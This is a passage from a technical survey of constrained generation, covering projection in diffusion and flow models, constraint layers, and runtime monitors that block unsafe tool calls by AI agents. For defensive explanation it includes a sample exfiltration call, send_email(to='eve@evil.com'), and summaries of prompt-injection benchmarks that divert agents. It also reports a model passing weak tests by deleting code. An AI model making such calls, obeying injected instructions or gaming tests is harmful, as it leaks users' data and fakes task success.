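*Does Fixing Break Security?* (Agyekum and Santos, 2026) examined 5,968 runs in which two older models, Gemini 2.0 Flash and Mistral Large, wrote configuration files for cloud services and revised them up to five times. In 13.8% of runs, at least one security check passed in one round and failed in the next. Many of these cases were ambiguous, because one check can apply to several parts of a file and fail for only some of them. Counting only checks that went from passing everywhere to failing everywhere reduces the figure to 3.3%.

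The average share of checks passed peaked at 83.4% after four revisions and fell to 82.6% after the fifth. The decline is small, and the two averages cover different sets of runs because successful runs stop early. But many studies report only the best result up to each round, which would hide any such decline.

One remedy is to tell a coding agent which tests its changes might affect. *TDAD* (Alonso, Yovine and Braberman, 2026) gave a small agent a list that matched each source file to its tests. The agent's changes broke 6.08% of previously passing tests without the list and 1.82% with it. Instructing the agent to write tests first, without giving it the list, raised the figure to 9.94%. With the list, the agent submitted fewer changes and solved 29% of the tasks instead of 31%.

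### The final check provides the guarantee

Any revision may break something that worked before, so earlier test results don't apply to the new version. The system has to run the complete check on the exact version it returns. As in generate and verify, a sound checker then guarantees that a version that passes satisfies the constraints, however it was revised.

A final check is useful even after an exact repair, because the integer program may contain a mistake, such as allowing flow to leave the locked door. A flood fill on the repaired level would catch any unplayable result almost instantly, so nobody would have to trust the solver or the flow equations.

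The model's own judgment is a poor substitute for this check. Cuadron and Gupta asked ten models to judge finished code, half of which was wrong, and the models were right only 53% of the time.

If the final check consists of tests, it guarantees only that the program passes them. *From Empirical Evaluation to Context-Aware Enhancement* (2025) attributed 23.73% of language models' failures to repair bugs to weak tests that accepted a wrong repair. In one case, two separate lines needed correcting. The model corrected one, but instead of correcting the other, it deleted the whole block of code that ran when a certain file existed. The program passed every test because none covered the case where the file exists.

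## Projection and built-in constraints for numerical outputs

Many generators produce lists of real numbers, such as the pixels of an image, the points on a robot's path, the entries of a medical table or the temperatures along a metal rod. A diffusion model generates all the numbers together, so there are no tokens for a mask to block.

Rejection sampling still works if the constraint is an inequality that the model often satisfies, but it fails for equalities. Suppose a model generates three percentages that must add up to 100. The total might be 99.7 or 100.2, but a continuous distribution normally gives exactly 100 with probability zero, however many samples are drawn. In *HardNet*, Min and Azizan (2024) used a penalty for violations to train a network to solve optimisation problems with 50 equations and 50 inequalities. The network satisfied nearly all the inequalities but none of the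 equations, which it missed by 0.1 on average.

### The nearest valid point

The numerical counterpart of repair is *projection*. The projection of an output x onto the set C of valid outputs is the point of C nearest to x:

P(x) = the point y in C that minimises ‖y − x‖²,

where ‖y − x‖ is the straight-line distance between the two points. A valid output is its own projection.

Suppose a model outputs two numbers whose sum must not exceed 2, and it returns (3, 1). The shortest way to the line x + y = 2 is at right angles to it, so projection lowers both numbers equally and gives (2, 0), at a distance of 1.41. The point (1, 1) is also valid, but its distance is 2. For a single linear inequality a·x ≤ b, where a is a list of weights, the formula is

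P(x) = x − a max(0, a·x − b) / ‖a‖².

In the example, a is (1, 1), b is 2 and ‖a‖² is 2. The sum is 2 too large, so the formula subtracts (1, 1).

How reliable projection is depends on the shape of C. A set is *convex* if the straight line between any two of its points stays inside the set, as in a box or a filled circle. If a convex set contains its boundary and at least one point, every x has exactly one nearest point in it. There can't be two, because the point halfway between them would also be valid and closer to x. A solver also can't get stuck at a worse solution, because any valid point that is nearer to x than all its valid neighbours is the nearest overall.

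The space around an obstacle is not convex. Suppose a robot must stay at least one metre from the centre of a pillar, and the model places it exactly at the centre. All points on the surrounding circle are equally near. A solver that increases x² + y² by following its slope may stop at the centre, where the slope is zero, and return an invalid position. With several obstacles, it may also return a valid path that is much longer than necessary.

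### Projected diffusion models

Christopher, Baek and Fioretto (2024), in *Constrained Synthesis with Projected Diffusion Models*, apply projection throughout generation. Each update of their model is

x ← P(x + γ s(x) + √(2γ) ε).

Here s(x) is the neural network's estimate of the direction in which x becomes more typical of the training data, γ is the step size and ε is fresh Gaussian noise. Every update ends with a projection, so the final output is valid as long as the last projection succeeds.

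A single projection after the last denoising step can also produce a valid output, but no steps remain to adapt the rest of the image to the part it changed. If the projection happens earlier, the remaining steps can make that adjustment.

One experiment generated microscope images of a material with a prescribed porosity, defined by how many pixels fall below a brightness threshold. The valid images don't form a convex set, but the nearest valid image is easy to find. If too few pixels are below the threshold, a program can darken the remaining pixels closest to it. Projecting at every step met the porosity target exactly, and the images were as realistic as those from a model that received the porosity as an input but often missed the target. Projecting only once, at the end, visibly reduced image quality.

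The method also worked for constraints that no training example satisfied. Christopher and colleagues trained a model on videos of objects falling under Earth's gravity, then required the positions to follow the Moon's gravity. Projection at every step put the object in the right place in each frame without spoiling the image. In a test with human figures, the generated bodies never sank into the floor or floated above it. They were slightly less realistic, scoring 0.71 compared with 0.63 for an unprojected model (lower is better).

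The hardest test was planning a path around obstacles absent from the training data. The table shows how often a single attempt produced a collision-free path.

| Method | First map | Second map |
|---|---|---|
| Diffusion model without projection | 77.1% | 53.3% |
| The same model, followed by an optimisation solver | 77.1% | 53.3% |
| Projection at every step | 100% | 100% |

The solver made no difference when it ran only once, on the finished path. Christopher and colleagues prove that their method always produces valid outputs for convex sets, but the set of collision-free paths isn't convex. The 100% success rate is therefore a measured result, and the method could still fail on another map.

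Projection also requires solving an optimisation problem at every update. Christopher and colleagues suggest saving time by projecting only in the later steps, or by starting each optimisation from the previous solution.

### Why projected samples gather on the boundary

Projection doesn't sample from the conditioned distribution g. If 30% of a model's outputs violate x + y ≤ 2, a single projection at the end moves that 30% onto the line x + y = 2. Under g, an output lies on that line with probability zero. The distribution of projected outputs has infinite Kullback–Leibler divergence from the original model, while g has the smallest divergence of any distribution that satisfies the constraint.

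Projecting at every step lets the model move away from the boundary again, but it can introduce other distortions. Rochman-Sharabi and Louppe (2026), in *Predict-Project-Renoise*, warn that repeated projection can reduce the variety of outputs by pulling samples towards the nearest valid points. They also point out that many constraints make sense only for finished outputs. For example, a law about the total energy of a fluid means little when the data are still mostly noise.

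Rochman-Sharabi and Louppe's method takes a noisy state and searches for a similar one whose denoised version satisfies the constraint. It then adds noise to that denoised version to return to the same noise level, and repeats this several times before moving to the next noise level. The fresh noise lets the sample leave the valid point it first reached. They prove that an ideal version of this loop converges to the correct distribution at each noise level. The practical version uses a single estimate instead of a random draw from the valid outputs, which leaves an error that more repetitions can't remove.

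Li, Alim and Azizan (2025), in *HardFlow*, argue against constraining the intermediate states, because only the final output has to be valid. Forcing every state into the valid set can rule out paths to better outputs. Their method instead slightly adjusts the model's steps so that the final state satisfies the constraint. *Constraint-Aware Flow Matching* (2026) attributes the loss of quality to projections being applied during sampling but not during training, and proposes training the model in a way that accounts for the constrained sampling process.

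### Flow models with physical laws as constraints

HardFlow uses *flow matching*, a close relative of diffusion. The network learns a velocity v(u, τ), and a program solves du/dτ = v(u, τ) from random noise at τ = 0 to a finished output at τ = 1. For a physical system, the output u might be the temperature at every point of a rod over time. Physical laws become equations of the form h(u) = 0. For example, one such equation requires the total heat in an insulated rod to stay constant.

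Utkarsh, Cai and colleagues (2025), in *Physics-Constrained Flow Matching*, enforce such equations on a model that has already been trained. At each time step, their method PCFM does the following:

1. It quickly follows the flow to the end to get a predicted output u₁.
2. It replaces u₁ by u₁ − Jᵀ(JJᵀ)⁻¹h(u₁), where J is the matrix of derivatives of h at u₁.
3. It returns to the next time step along the straight line between the original noise and the corrected output.
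4. It makes a further small adjustment that reduces the remaining violation without moving the state far.

If the finished output still violates the equations by more than a set tolerance, a solver projects it onto the valid set.

The formula in the second step gives the exact projection if the constraint is linear. Otherwise it gives a *Gauss–Newton* step, which treats the constraint as linear near the current point. For example, the constraint x² + y² = 1 describes a circle. Repeated steps from (2, 0) lead to (1.25, 0), (1.025, 0) and about (1.0003, 0). At (0, 0), however, all the derivatives are zero, so the formula divides by zero. *DiffSlack* (2026) uses such steps for nonlinear inequalities. It therefore trains its network with a penalty first and switches on the projection only in a second stage, when the outputs should be close to the valid set.

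Utkarsh and colleagues tested PCFM, which handles only equality constraints, on equations for heat, fluid flow and chemical reactions, among others. They report constraint errors of zero to within machine precision. For the heat equation, the error in the average of the generated solutions was also lower, at 0.0024 compared with 0.0456 for the unconstrained model.

A later comparison was much less favourable to PCFM. In *MintFlow*, Park, Kan and colleagues (2026) ran PCFM on their own version of the heat task. They simulated how heat would spread from the initial temperatures in each generated output, then measured how far the output was from the simulation.

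| Method | Constraint violation | Difference from simulation |
|---|---|---|
| Unconstrained model | 0.0052 | 0.056 |
| PCFM | 0.00000013 | 0.445 |
| MintFlow | 0.0000036 | 0.012 |

PCFM satisfied the constraints almost perfectly, yet its outputs were about eight times as far from the simulation as those of the unconstrained model. The constraints covered the initial temperatures, the boundary conditions and the total heat. An output can satisfy all of these even if heat moves through the rod in a physically impossible way.

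MintFlow searches for the smallest change to one intermediate state that leads the unmodified model to a valid output. It calculates this change with a linear approximation, so some constraint violation remains. If the violation is too large, MintFlow can repeat the correction. Park and colleagues acknowledge that PCFM is preferable if the only goal is to minimise the violation. The two teams set up their tests differently, and each team's method did best on most of the measures in that team's own tests.

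### When no projection is available

Projection requires a usable description of the valid set. *Integration Matters* (2026) points out that a designer can sometimes observe violations without a formula for what is valid. Even with a formula, projection can be impractical. For instance, if two balls overlap in one frame of a generated video, moving them apart in that frame may make their motion inconsistent with the frames before and after it.

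*Improved Constrained Generation by Bridging Pretrained Generative Models* (Liang, Naderiparizi and colleagues, 2026) uses fine-tuning for such cases. The method freezes a trained diffusion model and adds a small network to it. At each step, a program measures how badly the model's current estimate of the finished output violates the constraint and calculates how to change that estimate to reduce the violation. The small network learns to pass this information to the frozen model. The method also applies the correction directly to the model's output, more strongly as the noise disappears.

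Liang and colleagues' method reduced the rate of overlaps among ten balls bouncing in a box from 38.12% to 0.01%. In a traffic simulation, it reduced the share of vehicles that left the road from 8.12% to 0.44%, and collisions from 0.39% to 0.27%. A method that applied corrections without fine-tuning eliminated all measured violations for the balls, but its motions matched the training data less closely. Liang and colleagues acknowledge that their method may not eliminate every violation.

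Baldan, Guardone and Liu (2025), in *Physics vs Distributions*, also account for physical laws during training. They combine the updates for physical accuracy and for resemblance to the data so that they don't conflict. Generation then needs no extra corrections, but like the training penalties discussed earlier, this method doesn't guarantee that every output obeys the physical laws.

### Networks that satisfy a constraint by construction

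A designer can also end the network with a function that returns only valid values. The outputs are then valid whatever numbers the rest of the network produces, even before training.

For proportions, the softmax is such a function, because its outputs are positive and add up to one. But they can never be exactly zero, so the softmax can't exactly represent a recipe that leaves out an ingredient. Projection can produce zeros. For example, projecting 2, 1 and −1 onto the set of valid proportions gives 1, 0 and 0. *SLP-ProbHard* (2026) notes that efficient algorithms exist for this projection and for projecting onto lists in ascending order.

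A change of variables is often enough to enforce linear equalities. If three numbers must add up to 100, the network can produce the first two, and the program subtracts them from 100 to get the third. This guarantees the total, but the third number may be negative.

The method can also break down if the equation depends on the network's input. Min and Azizan give the example

t y₁ + (t − 1) y₂ = 1,

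where t is the input and y₁ and y₂ are the outputs. A network could predict y₁ and solve for y₂, but at t = 1 this means dividing by zero. Predicting y₂ and solving for y₁ fails at t = 0.

### HardNet: a final layer for linear constraints

HardNet can handle several linear constraints at once, including ones that change with the input. Each constraint sets a lower and an upper limit for a weighted sum of the outputs. If A is the matrix of weights and l and u are the lists of limits, the final layer computes

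P(y) = y + A⁺ [max(0, l − Ay) − max(0, Ay − u)], where A⁺ = Aᵀ(AAᵀ)⁻¹.

The square brackets contain the size of each violation. Multiplying by A⁺ turns these into a change to the output that moves every violated sum exactly to its limit and leaves the other sums unchanged, so fixing one constraint can't break another.

The layer doesn't always return the nearest valid point. Suppose the output is again (3, 1) and the constraints are x + y ≤ 2 and x ≤ 3. The second constraint already holds, so the layer keeps x at 3 and returns (3, −1), but the nearest valid point is still (2, 0).

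The formula works only if valid outputs exist and the rows of A are linearly independent, so there can't be more weighted sums than outputs. It therefore can't handle even a triangle such as x ≥ 0, y ≥ 0 and x + y ≤ 2, which limits three sums of two outputs. For such sets, Min and Azizan suggest using a general convex solver as the final layer, which is slower.

The layer is in place during training, so the network learns to work with it. On the optimisation problems described earlier, an ordinary network violated all 50 equations and an average of 12 inequalities, while HardNet had no measurable violations. HardNet's solutions were slightly worse than those of a conventional solver (−14.10 compared with −14.28, where lower is better), but it took 7 milliseconds, compared with 1,182 for the solver.

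HardNet also met its constraints on inputs outside the training range. Min and Azizan trained networks on inputs between −1.2 and 1.2 and tested them between −2 and 2. The largest constraint violation averaged 3.16 for an ordinary network, 3.70 for one trained with a penalty and zero for HardNet.

### Constraint layers for synthetic tables

Hospitals and banks can share data or train other models using synthetic tables, which resemble real records without describing real people. *How Realistic Is Your Synthetic Data?* (Stoian, Dyrmishi et al., 2024) introduces a constraint layer for models that generate such tables. One constraint, from a medical dataset, requires a patient's highest haemoglobin level to be at least as high as the lowest.

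The layer goes through the columns in a fixed order. For each column, it works out the lowest and highest values that the constraints allow, given the columns it has already processed. It then replaces the model's value xᵢ by

min(max(xᵢ, lowest allowed value), highest allowed value).

Processing one column at a time could leave a later column with no valid value. Suppose column 1 must be at least as large as column 2, column 2 must be above 5, and the model generates 3 for both. If the layer left column 1 at 3, no value for column 2 would satisfy both constraints. The layer avoids this by combining the constraints in advance to derive that column 1 must also be above 5. It then raises both values to just above 5.

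Stoian and colleagues tested five models on six datasets with up to 31 constraints each. Without the layer, between 3% and 100% of the generated rows violated at least one constraint, and the rate was above 50% in more than half of the 30 model-dataset combinations. With the layer, the rate was 0% in every combination.

Training with the layer made the generated data more useful for training other models, by up to 6.5 percentage points. Adding the layer only after training had little effect on data quality but still guaranteed that the outputs met the constraints. Generating 1,000 rows took at most 0.27 seconds longer with the layer. The method handles only linear inequalities, and the number of combined constraints can grow exponentially in the worst case, although this didn't happen in the tests.

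### Rounding

These guarantees assume exact arithmetic, but computers round numbers. A 32-bit floating-point number has only about seven significant digits, so a projected output can still violate an equation by a tiny amount, as PCFM's outputs did in tests by Park and colleagues.

To satisfy a strict inequality such as "above 5", Stoian and colleagues start from 5 and add the smallest positive number the computer can represent. Taken literally, this would fail, because the sum rounds back to 5. A program should instead use the next representable number after 5.

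For other inequalities, a designer can leave a margin, for example by projecting onto x + y ≤ 1.999 when the real limit is 2. An equality leaves no room for a margin, so the specification has to state a tolerance. Rochman-Sharabi and Louppe count an output as valid if its measured violation is at most 0.0004 in one test and 0.000004 in another. A checker can then test the finished output against the tolerance and reject it if a solver stopped too early. This check is especially important for non-convex sets.

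## Enforcing safety rules on the actions of AI agents

An AI agent's output takes effect one action at a time. An agent that tidies a company's files may copy a folder, edit the copy and delete the original, and a check on its final report would come too late to save the original. A *runtime monitor* is a program between the agent and its tools that examines each action before it takes effect and can block or change it.

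An agent's actions are easier to constrain than its text. *Progent* (Shi, He et al., 2025) points out that an agent affects the outside world only through tool calls, each consisting of a name and typed arguments. The agent's reasoning may express a plan to email customer data to a stranger in any words, or not mention it at all. But in the call `send_email(to="eve@evil.com")`, the recipient is a separate field that a program can compare with a list of permitted addresses. The comparison gives the same result whether the model made a mistake or followed an instruction hidden in an email.

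### Safety and liveness properties

A rule for an agent is a condition on its *run*, the whole sequence of its actions. "Never delete a file without a backup" is a *safety property* because every run that violates it contains a point, here the deletion, after which no later action can repair the violation. "Eventually reply to the user" is a *liveness property*, since the agent could still reply no matter how long it has been silent.

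A property is a safety property if every run that violates it has a finite beginning that cannot be continued into a run that satisfies it. It is a liveness property if every finite beginning of a run can be continued into a run that satisfies it. In 1985, Bowen Alpern and Fred Schneider proved that every property is a combination of a safety property and a liveness property. For example, "back up the file and then delete it" combines the safety property that no deletion comes before a backup with the liveness property that a backup followed by a deletion eventually happens.

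### What a monitor can enforce

In 2000, Schneider studied monitors that can only halt a run. If such a monitor must never interrupt a valid run, it can enforce only safety properties. For any other property, there is a run that violates it even though every beginning of that run could still have led to a valid one. Since the monitor can check only the actions so far, it must allow each action and therefore the whole run.

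A monitor also cannot enforce every safety property, because it cannot detect every kind of violation. "Never start a program that would run forever" is a safety property, but no monitor can check it for every program, since that would require solving the halting problem.

A deadline turns a liveness property into a safety property. For example, the rule "Reply within ten actions" is permanently violated once the agent has taken ten actions without replying. A monitor can prevent the violation by halting the run after the ninth action, but the user still gets no reply.

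Monitors can enforce more rules if they can change an agent's sequence of actions as well as halt it. In 2005, Jay Ligatti, Lujo Bauer and David Walker described *edit automata*, which can suppress actions and insert new ones. For example, a rule might require that a confirmation eventually follow every refund. A monitor that can only halt the agent can't enforce this rule, because the confirmation could still come later. An edit automaton can hold back the refund until the agent writes the confirmation, and then carry out both. If the agent never writes one, the refund never happens and the rule still holds. In general, edit automata can enforce a property if every valid endless run satisfies it at infinitely many points, because the monitor can release the held actions at those points. The method is less useful if the agent needs the result of the held action, such as a refund number to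 put in the confirmation.

Monitors for language model agents usually reject a call, tell the model why and let it try again. This blocks the action without ending the run, but it can't force the agent to do anything. *Symbolic Temporal Supervision of LLM Agents Using Contracts* (Xiao, Liu and Nuzzo, 2026) handles required actions in two ways. If a rule requires a certain call next, the monitor rejects every other call. If a required action has no deadline, the monitor reminds the agent at the end of the session and records a violation if the agent still doesn't act.

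### From a sentence to an automaton

A more careful version of the backup rule is "never delete a file unless the agent has backed it up since the last change". *Temporal logic* can express this, because it adds operators for the order of events to ordinary logic:

- G p: p holds at every step from now on.
- F p: p holds now or at some later step.
- X p: p holds at the next step.
- p U q: p holds until q does, and q eventually does.
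- p W q: p holds until q does, or forever if q never does.

The last two differ only in a liveness property, since p U q is the same as (p W q) and F q.

Let w, b and d stand for writing to the file, backing it up and deleting it. The rule is then

(¬d W b) ∧ G(w → (¬d W b)).

The first part forbids deletion before the first backup. The second forbids it after every change until the next backup. A standard construction turns the formula into a finite automaton:

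| State | After a backup | After a write | After a deletion |
|---|---|---|---|
| Unprotected (start) | protected | unprotected | violation |
| Protected | protected | unprotected | protected |

Other calls leave the state unchanged. The monitor looks up each proposed call and blocks it if it leads to a violation. Here is a short run:

| Proposed call | State before | Decision | State after |
|---|---|---|---|
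| `read` | unprotected | allow | unprotected |
| `backup` | unprotected | allow | protected |
| `write` | protected | allow | unprotected |
| `delete` | unprotected | block | unprotected |
| `backup` | unprotected | allow | protected |
| `delete` | protected | allow | protected |

The agent backed up the file before first trying to delete it, but the backup was out of date. The monitor needs a separate state for each file, and it should switch a file's state to "protected" only after the backup tool reports success. Each check takes one table lookup, however long the run.

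Rules of this kind can also save time. In *Learning Context-Free Grammars for Grammar-Constrained Decoding via Declarative Agentic Programming with Guarantees*, Cheang, Hulette and colleagues (2026) built an agent that learns the grammar of a programming language from examples. One rule forbids the agent to test the same grammar twice unless the examples have changed. Another requires its next action to be returning a grammar once the time limit has passed. If the model chooses a forbidden action, the program prompts it to choose again. The agent was 3.8 times as fast with such rules as without them. The precision of its grammars did not fall significantly, but their recall fell sharply for one of the three languages.

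### Shielding in reinforcement learning

Blocking a deletion is enough to protect a file, but in the physical world a violation can become unavoidable long before it happens. For example, a drone may still be flying when its battery is too low to get it home.

*Shielding*, which Mohammed Alshiekh and colleagues proposed in 2018, addresses this problem for *reinforcement learning*, in which an agent learns from rewards by trial and error. Before training, a program uses a model of the environment to find the states from which the agent can stay safe whatever the environment does. During training and afterwards, the shield allows only actions that keep the agent in those states.

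In a simple version, the drone flies one kilometre per step, either away from its base or towards it. Each kilometre costs one or two units of charge, depending on the wind, and the drone must never run out before it lands. The program finds the safe states as follows:

1. It removes all states in which the drone has already run out.
2. It removes every state in which each available action could lead to a removed state.
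3. It repeats the second step until nothing changes.

The program removes the state in which the drone is one kilometre from base with one unit of charge left, because it could run out in either direction. It also removes the state two kilometres away with three units, because a headwind on the way home could leave the drone in the first state. This leaves the states with at least two units of charge per kilometre from base. If the drone is two kilometres away with seven units, the shield blocks another step outwards because the drone could arrive at three kilometres with only five, but it allows the step with eight units.

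The guarantee holds only if the model includes every effect the wind can have on the drone, though it doesn't have to predict which one will occur. If a storm makes the drone use three units to fly one kilometre and the model doesn't include that possibility, the drone may crash even though the shield worked as designed.

Language model agents rarely have such a model of their environment, because nobody can list everything that a website or a customer might do. Their monitors therefore check whether an action breaks the rules, given what has happened so far in the run, without calculating how the environment might respond.

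### Rules about single actions

Progent, a system by Shi and colleagues, uses rules that allow or forbid a tool call depending on its arguments. For example, a rule might allow a Slack message only if the recipient is Alice. Rules that forbid a call take priority over rules that allow it, and Progent also blocks any call that matches no rule. A language model writes the rules for each task based on the user's request.

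AgentDojo is a benchmark in which emails and other outside data contain instructions meant to divert the agent. On this benchmark, Progent reduced the share of successful attacks against a GPT-4o agent from 39.9% to 1.0%, and the agent completed about as many tasks as before. On Agent Security Bench (ASB), the share fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Most of the remaining attacks used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate ones. Hand-written rules eliminated these as well.

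*AgentSpec* (Wang, Poskitt and Sun, 2025) uses rules that each have a triggering event, a condition to check, and a response. One rule for a household robot applies whenever the robot is about to pour something, and stops it if the target should not get wet. A rule can also respond by asking the user, having the model reconsider, or carrying out a different action. In the driving tests, when another vehicle was less than ten metres ahead, one rule changed the car's distance settings for following, yielding and overtaking instead of stopping the car.

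The robot was given dangerous instructions in ten categories, such as instructions that would break something. Without AgentSpec, it carried out up to 79% of the instructions in a category, and with AgentSpec it carried out none. The share of safe tasks it completed fell from 58.6% to 54.3%. With AgentSpec, the car obeyed the law in all eight driving scenarios.

Results for an agent that writes and runs Python code were less clear. Given 750 risky instructions, the agent tried to run 422 programs, and the rules flagged 333 of them. The rules flagged none of the 58 programs in two categories because the agent had written code without the relevant flaw. Excluding those two categories, the rules flagged 91% of the programs. Wang and colleagues inspected the 333 flagged programs and judged 58 harmless.

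Checking a condition took one to three milliseconds, while an average run took 10 to 25 seconds. The delay is longer if the response is to ask a person or a language model.

### Rules about the order of actions

Many rules depend on earlier actions. For example, under a limit of two transfers, each transfer is acceptable by itself, but a third breaks the rule.

*Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang et al., 2025) introduces Agent-C, whose rules can require that one tool call come before another. Rules can also refer to the results of earlier calls and to the tools' data. For example, the agent must identify the user before looking up an order, and the order must belong to that user. For each proposed call, a solver looks for a continuation of the run that satisfies all the rules, and the call goes ahead only if the solver finds one.

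If the model's token probabilities are available, Agent-C enforces the rules while the model is writing a tool call, and backtracks only as far as necessary, for example to the start of the call. Otherwise, it rejects the finished call and prompts the model again. On retail tasks, a small open model completed 42.1% of tasks with backtracking and 36.5% with repeated prompting, and it wrote 40% fewer tokens with backtracking.

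Kamath and colleagues tested Agent-C on τ-bench, in which agents serve customers of a shop or an airline under a written policy. On the retail tasks, Qwen3-32B followed the policy in 37.7% of runs without enforcement, 84.1% with AgentSpec rules that Kamath and colleagues wrote for the comparison, and 100% with Agent-C. Claude Sonnet 4.5's rate rose from 93.0% to 100%. Its share of completed tasks also rose, from 76.5% to 80.5%, but a task counted as completed only if the agent followed the policy. Qwen3-32B's average time per task increased from 333 to 480 seconds.

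Xiao and colleagues' system, ContrAgent, uses temporal logic and automata, much like the backup example. Each rule is a *contract* that pairs an assumption about the environment with a guarantee that the agent must meet if the assumption holds. A contract might assume that a policy service supplies valid refund limits and require the agent to stay within them. When something goes wrong, the monitor can report whether the agent or the environment was at fault.

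ContrAgent was tested on SOPBench, which covers procedures in seven settings, including a bank, a hotel and a library. With Gemini 2.5 Flash as the agent, ContrAgent raised the share of forbidden requests correctly refused from 32% to 98%, while the share of permitted tasks completed fell from 91% to 90%. The remaining 2% of forbidden requests were university tasks in which the agent made a permitted change that the benchmark could not distinguish from the forbidden one. ContrAgent added 0.135 seconds to a typical task of about two seconds.

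With the same procedures in its prompt, the agent refused 94% of forbidden requests but completed only 64% of permitted tasks, and only 18% when the procedure had ten or more constraints. With a weaker model, the agent refused only 45% of forbidden requests when the procedures were in the prompt, but still refused 98% with ContrAgent.

Agent-C's slower method has an advantage when rules interact. For example, one rule might require a confirmation email after every refund, while another forbids emails to customers who have opted out. Refunding a customer who has opted out breaks neither rule immediately, but nothing the agent does afterwards can satisfy both, which is the same kind of dead end that can occur in constrained decoding. Agent-C's solver checks all the rules together, so it would block the refund. ContrAgent checks each contract separately, so it would allow the refund and only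 then detect that the agent can't send the required email without breaking the other rule.

### What happens after a violation

How a monitor responds to a violation strongly affects how many tasks the agent completes. *VeriGuard* (Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues, 2025) compared five responses on ASB with Gemini 2.5 Flash. In this system, a language model writes a short program that decides whether an action is allowed, and a verifier proves that the program meets a formal specification.

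| Response to a violation | Successful attacks | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| End the whole task | 0% | 0% |
| Block the action | 0% | 38.1% |
| Block only the offending tool call | 0% | 44.6% |
| Explain the violation and ask for a new plan | 11.9% | 62.1% |
| Explain the violation and block the call | 0% | 63.3% |

An explanation helps the agent find another way to finish the task, but unless the forbidden call is blocked, the agent can still make it.

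The next table compares results with and without each system. The benchmarks and measures differ, so it doesn't show which system is best.

| System | Test | Violations | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Progent | AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 39.9% → 1.0% of attacks | about the same |
| AgentSpec | Household robot | up to 79% → 0% of dangerous tasks | 58.6% → 54.3% |
| Agent-C | τ-bench retail, Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 7.0% → 0% of runs | 76.5% → 80.5% |
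| ContrAgent | SOPBench, Gemini 2.5 Flash | 68% → 2% of forbidden requests | 91% → 90% |
| VeriGuard | ASB, Gemini 2.5 Flash | 51.9% → 0% of attacks | 42.1% → 63.3% |

VeriGuard's gain in completed tasks is so large because the attacks often stopped the unprotected agent from doing its work.

### Conditions of the guarantee

A monitor guarantees a rule only if every relevant action passes through it. Progent can run as a separate program between the agent and its tools, without changes to the agent, but Shi and colleagues warn that this version misses tools built into the agent. None of these monitors prevents harm that the agent does in its written reply, as *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) notes for Progent. When Xiao and colleagues replayed recorded AgentDojo runs, 82% of the attacks that ContrAgent missed involved no malicious tool call.

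A tool that runs code leaves another gap, because one call can contain any number of actions. AgentSpec's rules check the code before it runs, for example by searching for a command that deletes files. But a program can delete files in many other ways, so code without that command may still delete them. A monitor that checks each file operation as the program runs would be more reliable.

The monitor also needs accurate, current information about the state of the world. Agent-C's guarantee assumes that no other program changes the tools' data, because otherwise an order could change between the check and the action. ContrAgent relies on the surrounding software to report events correctly. In the backup example, the rule would fail if the backup tool reported success after saving an empty file.

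Finally, the formal rule has to cover the cases that the written policy covers. τ-bench requires a refund to go to the original payment method or to an existing gift card in the customer's account. The formal version in Kamath and colleagues' paper accepts the original method or any method whose name contains "gift_card", and doesn't by itself check whether the card belongs to the customer.

When no rule applies to a call, Progent blocks it, which may prevent the agent from completing its task, whereas AgentSpec allows it, even though the call may be harmful. In both systems, the rules may not capture everything that people mean by harm.

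### Rules that need a learned judgement

Some rules contain words that no program can check exactly, such as "confidential" or "suspicious". If a system uses a language model to check whether such a word applies, it can no longer guarantee that the rule is enforced, because the model, like any learned checker, has an error rate.

VeriGuard's programs are formally verified, but a language model extracts their arguments from the agent's text, and this reliance on the model's judgement can be easy to overlook. Miculicich and colleagues give the model an example in which the text asks for an email to "Dona Jhonson" without an address, and the expected extraction is `dona@example.com`. If the agent then writes to a different address, a program that enforces a rule against emails outside the company will have checked the wrong address.

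On a test of access to hospital records, VeriGuard made no mistakes. On a test of web tasks with GPT-4o, it caught 99% of violations, but the rules permitted about 9% of the actions it blocked. It stopped every attack in the ASB benchmark, as did a language model that judged each action against the same policy. However, the agent completed 63.3% of tasks with VeriGuard and 40.2% with the language model judge.

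The chance of wrongly blocking an action grows with the length of the task. If a judge wrongly blocks 1% of permitted actions, independently of one another, a task with 50 permitted actions has a 39% chance of at least one wrong block. Xiao and colleagues also tested a language model as a judge on SOPBench. The judge matched ContrAgent's 98% on forbidden requests, but the agent completed only 24% of permitted tasks under it.

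A learned model does not weaken the guarantee if it can only add restrictions. Progent applies this idea when it updates its rules during a task. After the agent has looked up its user's Slack name, for example, the language model may propose allowing messages only to that name. A solver then checks whether the new rules allow any call that the old ones did not. If they don't, Progent adopts them automatically, and a mistake by the model can at worst block something useful. If they do, someone has to approve the change. Only 6% of updates on AgentDojo needed approval.

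Progent's main results came from a setting that approved every change automatically, so they don't reflect this protection. When a person reviewed the initial rules and every proposed expansion, the share of attacks that succeeded fell from 1.0% to zero.

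## Whether the written constraint is the property that was wanted

The refund rule from τ-bench accepts any payment method whose name contains "gift_card", even when a monitor enforces the rule perfectly. In *The proof is in the spec*, an article for the verification company Runtime Verification, Tolmach and Klaus (2026) distinguish two questions that no proof checker can answer: whether the formal model matches the real system, and whether the specification expresses what people want.

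A specification can miss what people want. For example, if the specification for a sorting program requires only that the output be in ascending order, a program that always returns an empty list satisfies it, and a proof checker would accept a proof that it does. The specification must also require the output to contain the same items as the input. Errors in a formal model of a large existing system can be harder to notice, because finding them means comparing the model with that system.

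### Models that do not match the real system

Companies such as Amazon and Microsoft check critical systems with TLA+, a language for describing a system's possible states and the actions that move it between them. A program can then search the model for states that break a rule. *SysMoBench* (2025) is a benchmark that tests whether AI can write such a model for an existing system. *Can LLMs model real-world systems in TLA+?*, an article published by the operating systems research society SIGOPS, presents newer results from the benchmark's developers.

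One of the benchmark's 11 systems is ZooKeeper, which coordinates groups of servers and has them elect a leader. When a server changes its vote, ZooKeeper overwrites the old one. A model written by Claude Sonnet kept both votes, so it could count votes that no longer existed. This kind of error can add states that the real system never enters, which can cause false alarms. The model also ignored any message from a newer election round, whereas a real server updates its own round number and then processes the message. The model therefore left out states that ZooKeeper enters in every election, and a search that never reaches those states can miss a bug.

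To measure such errors, the benchmark records real runs of a system, cuts them into single steps and checks whether the formal model allows each step. Leading language models scored near 100% on syntax but averaged about 46% on this conformance test. They averaged 41% on a further test of whether the formal model has the safety and liveness properties it should, with individual scores from 16% to 81%.

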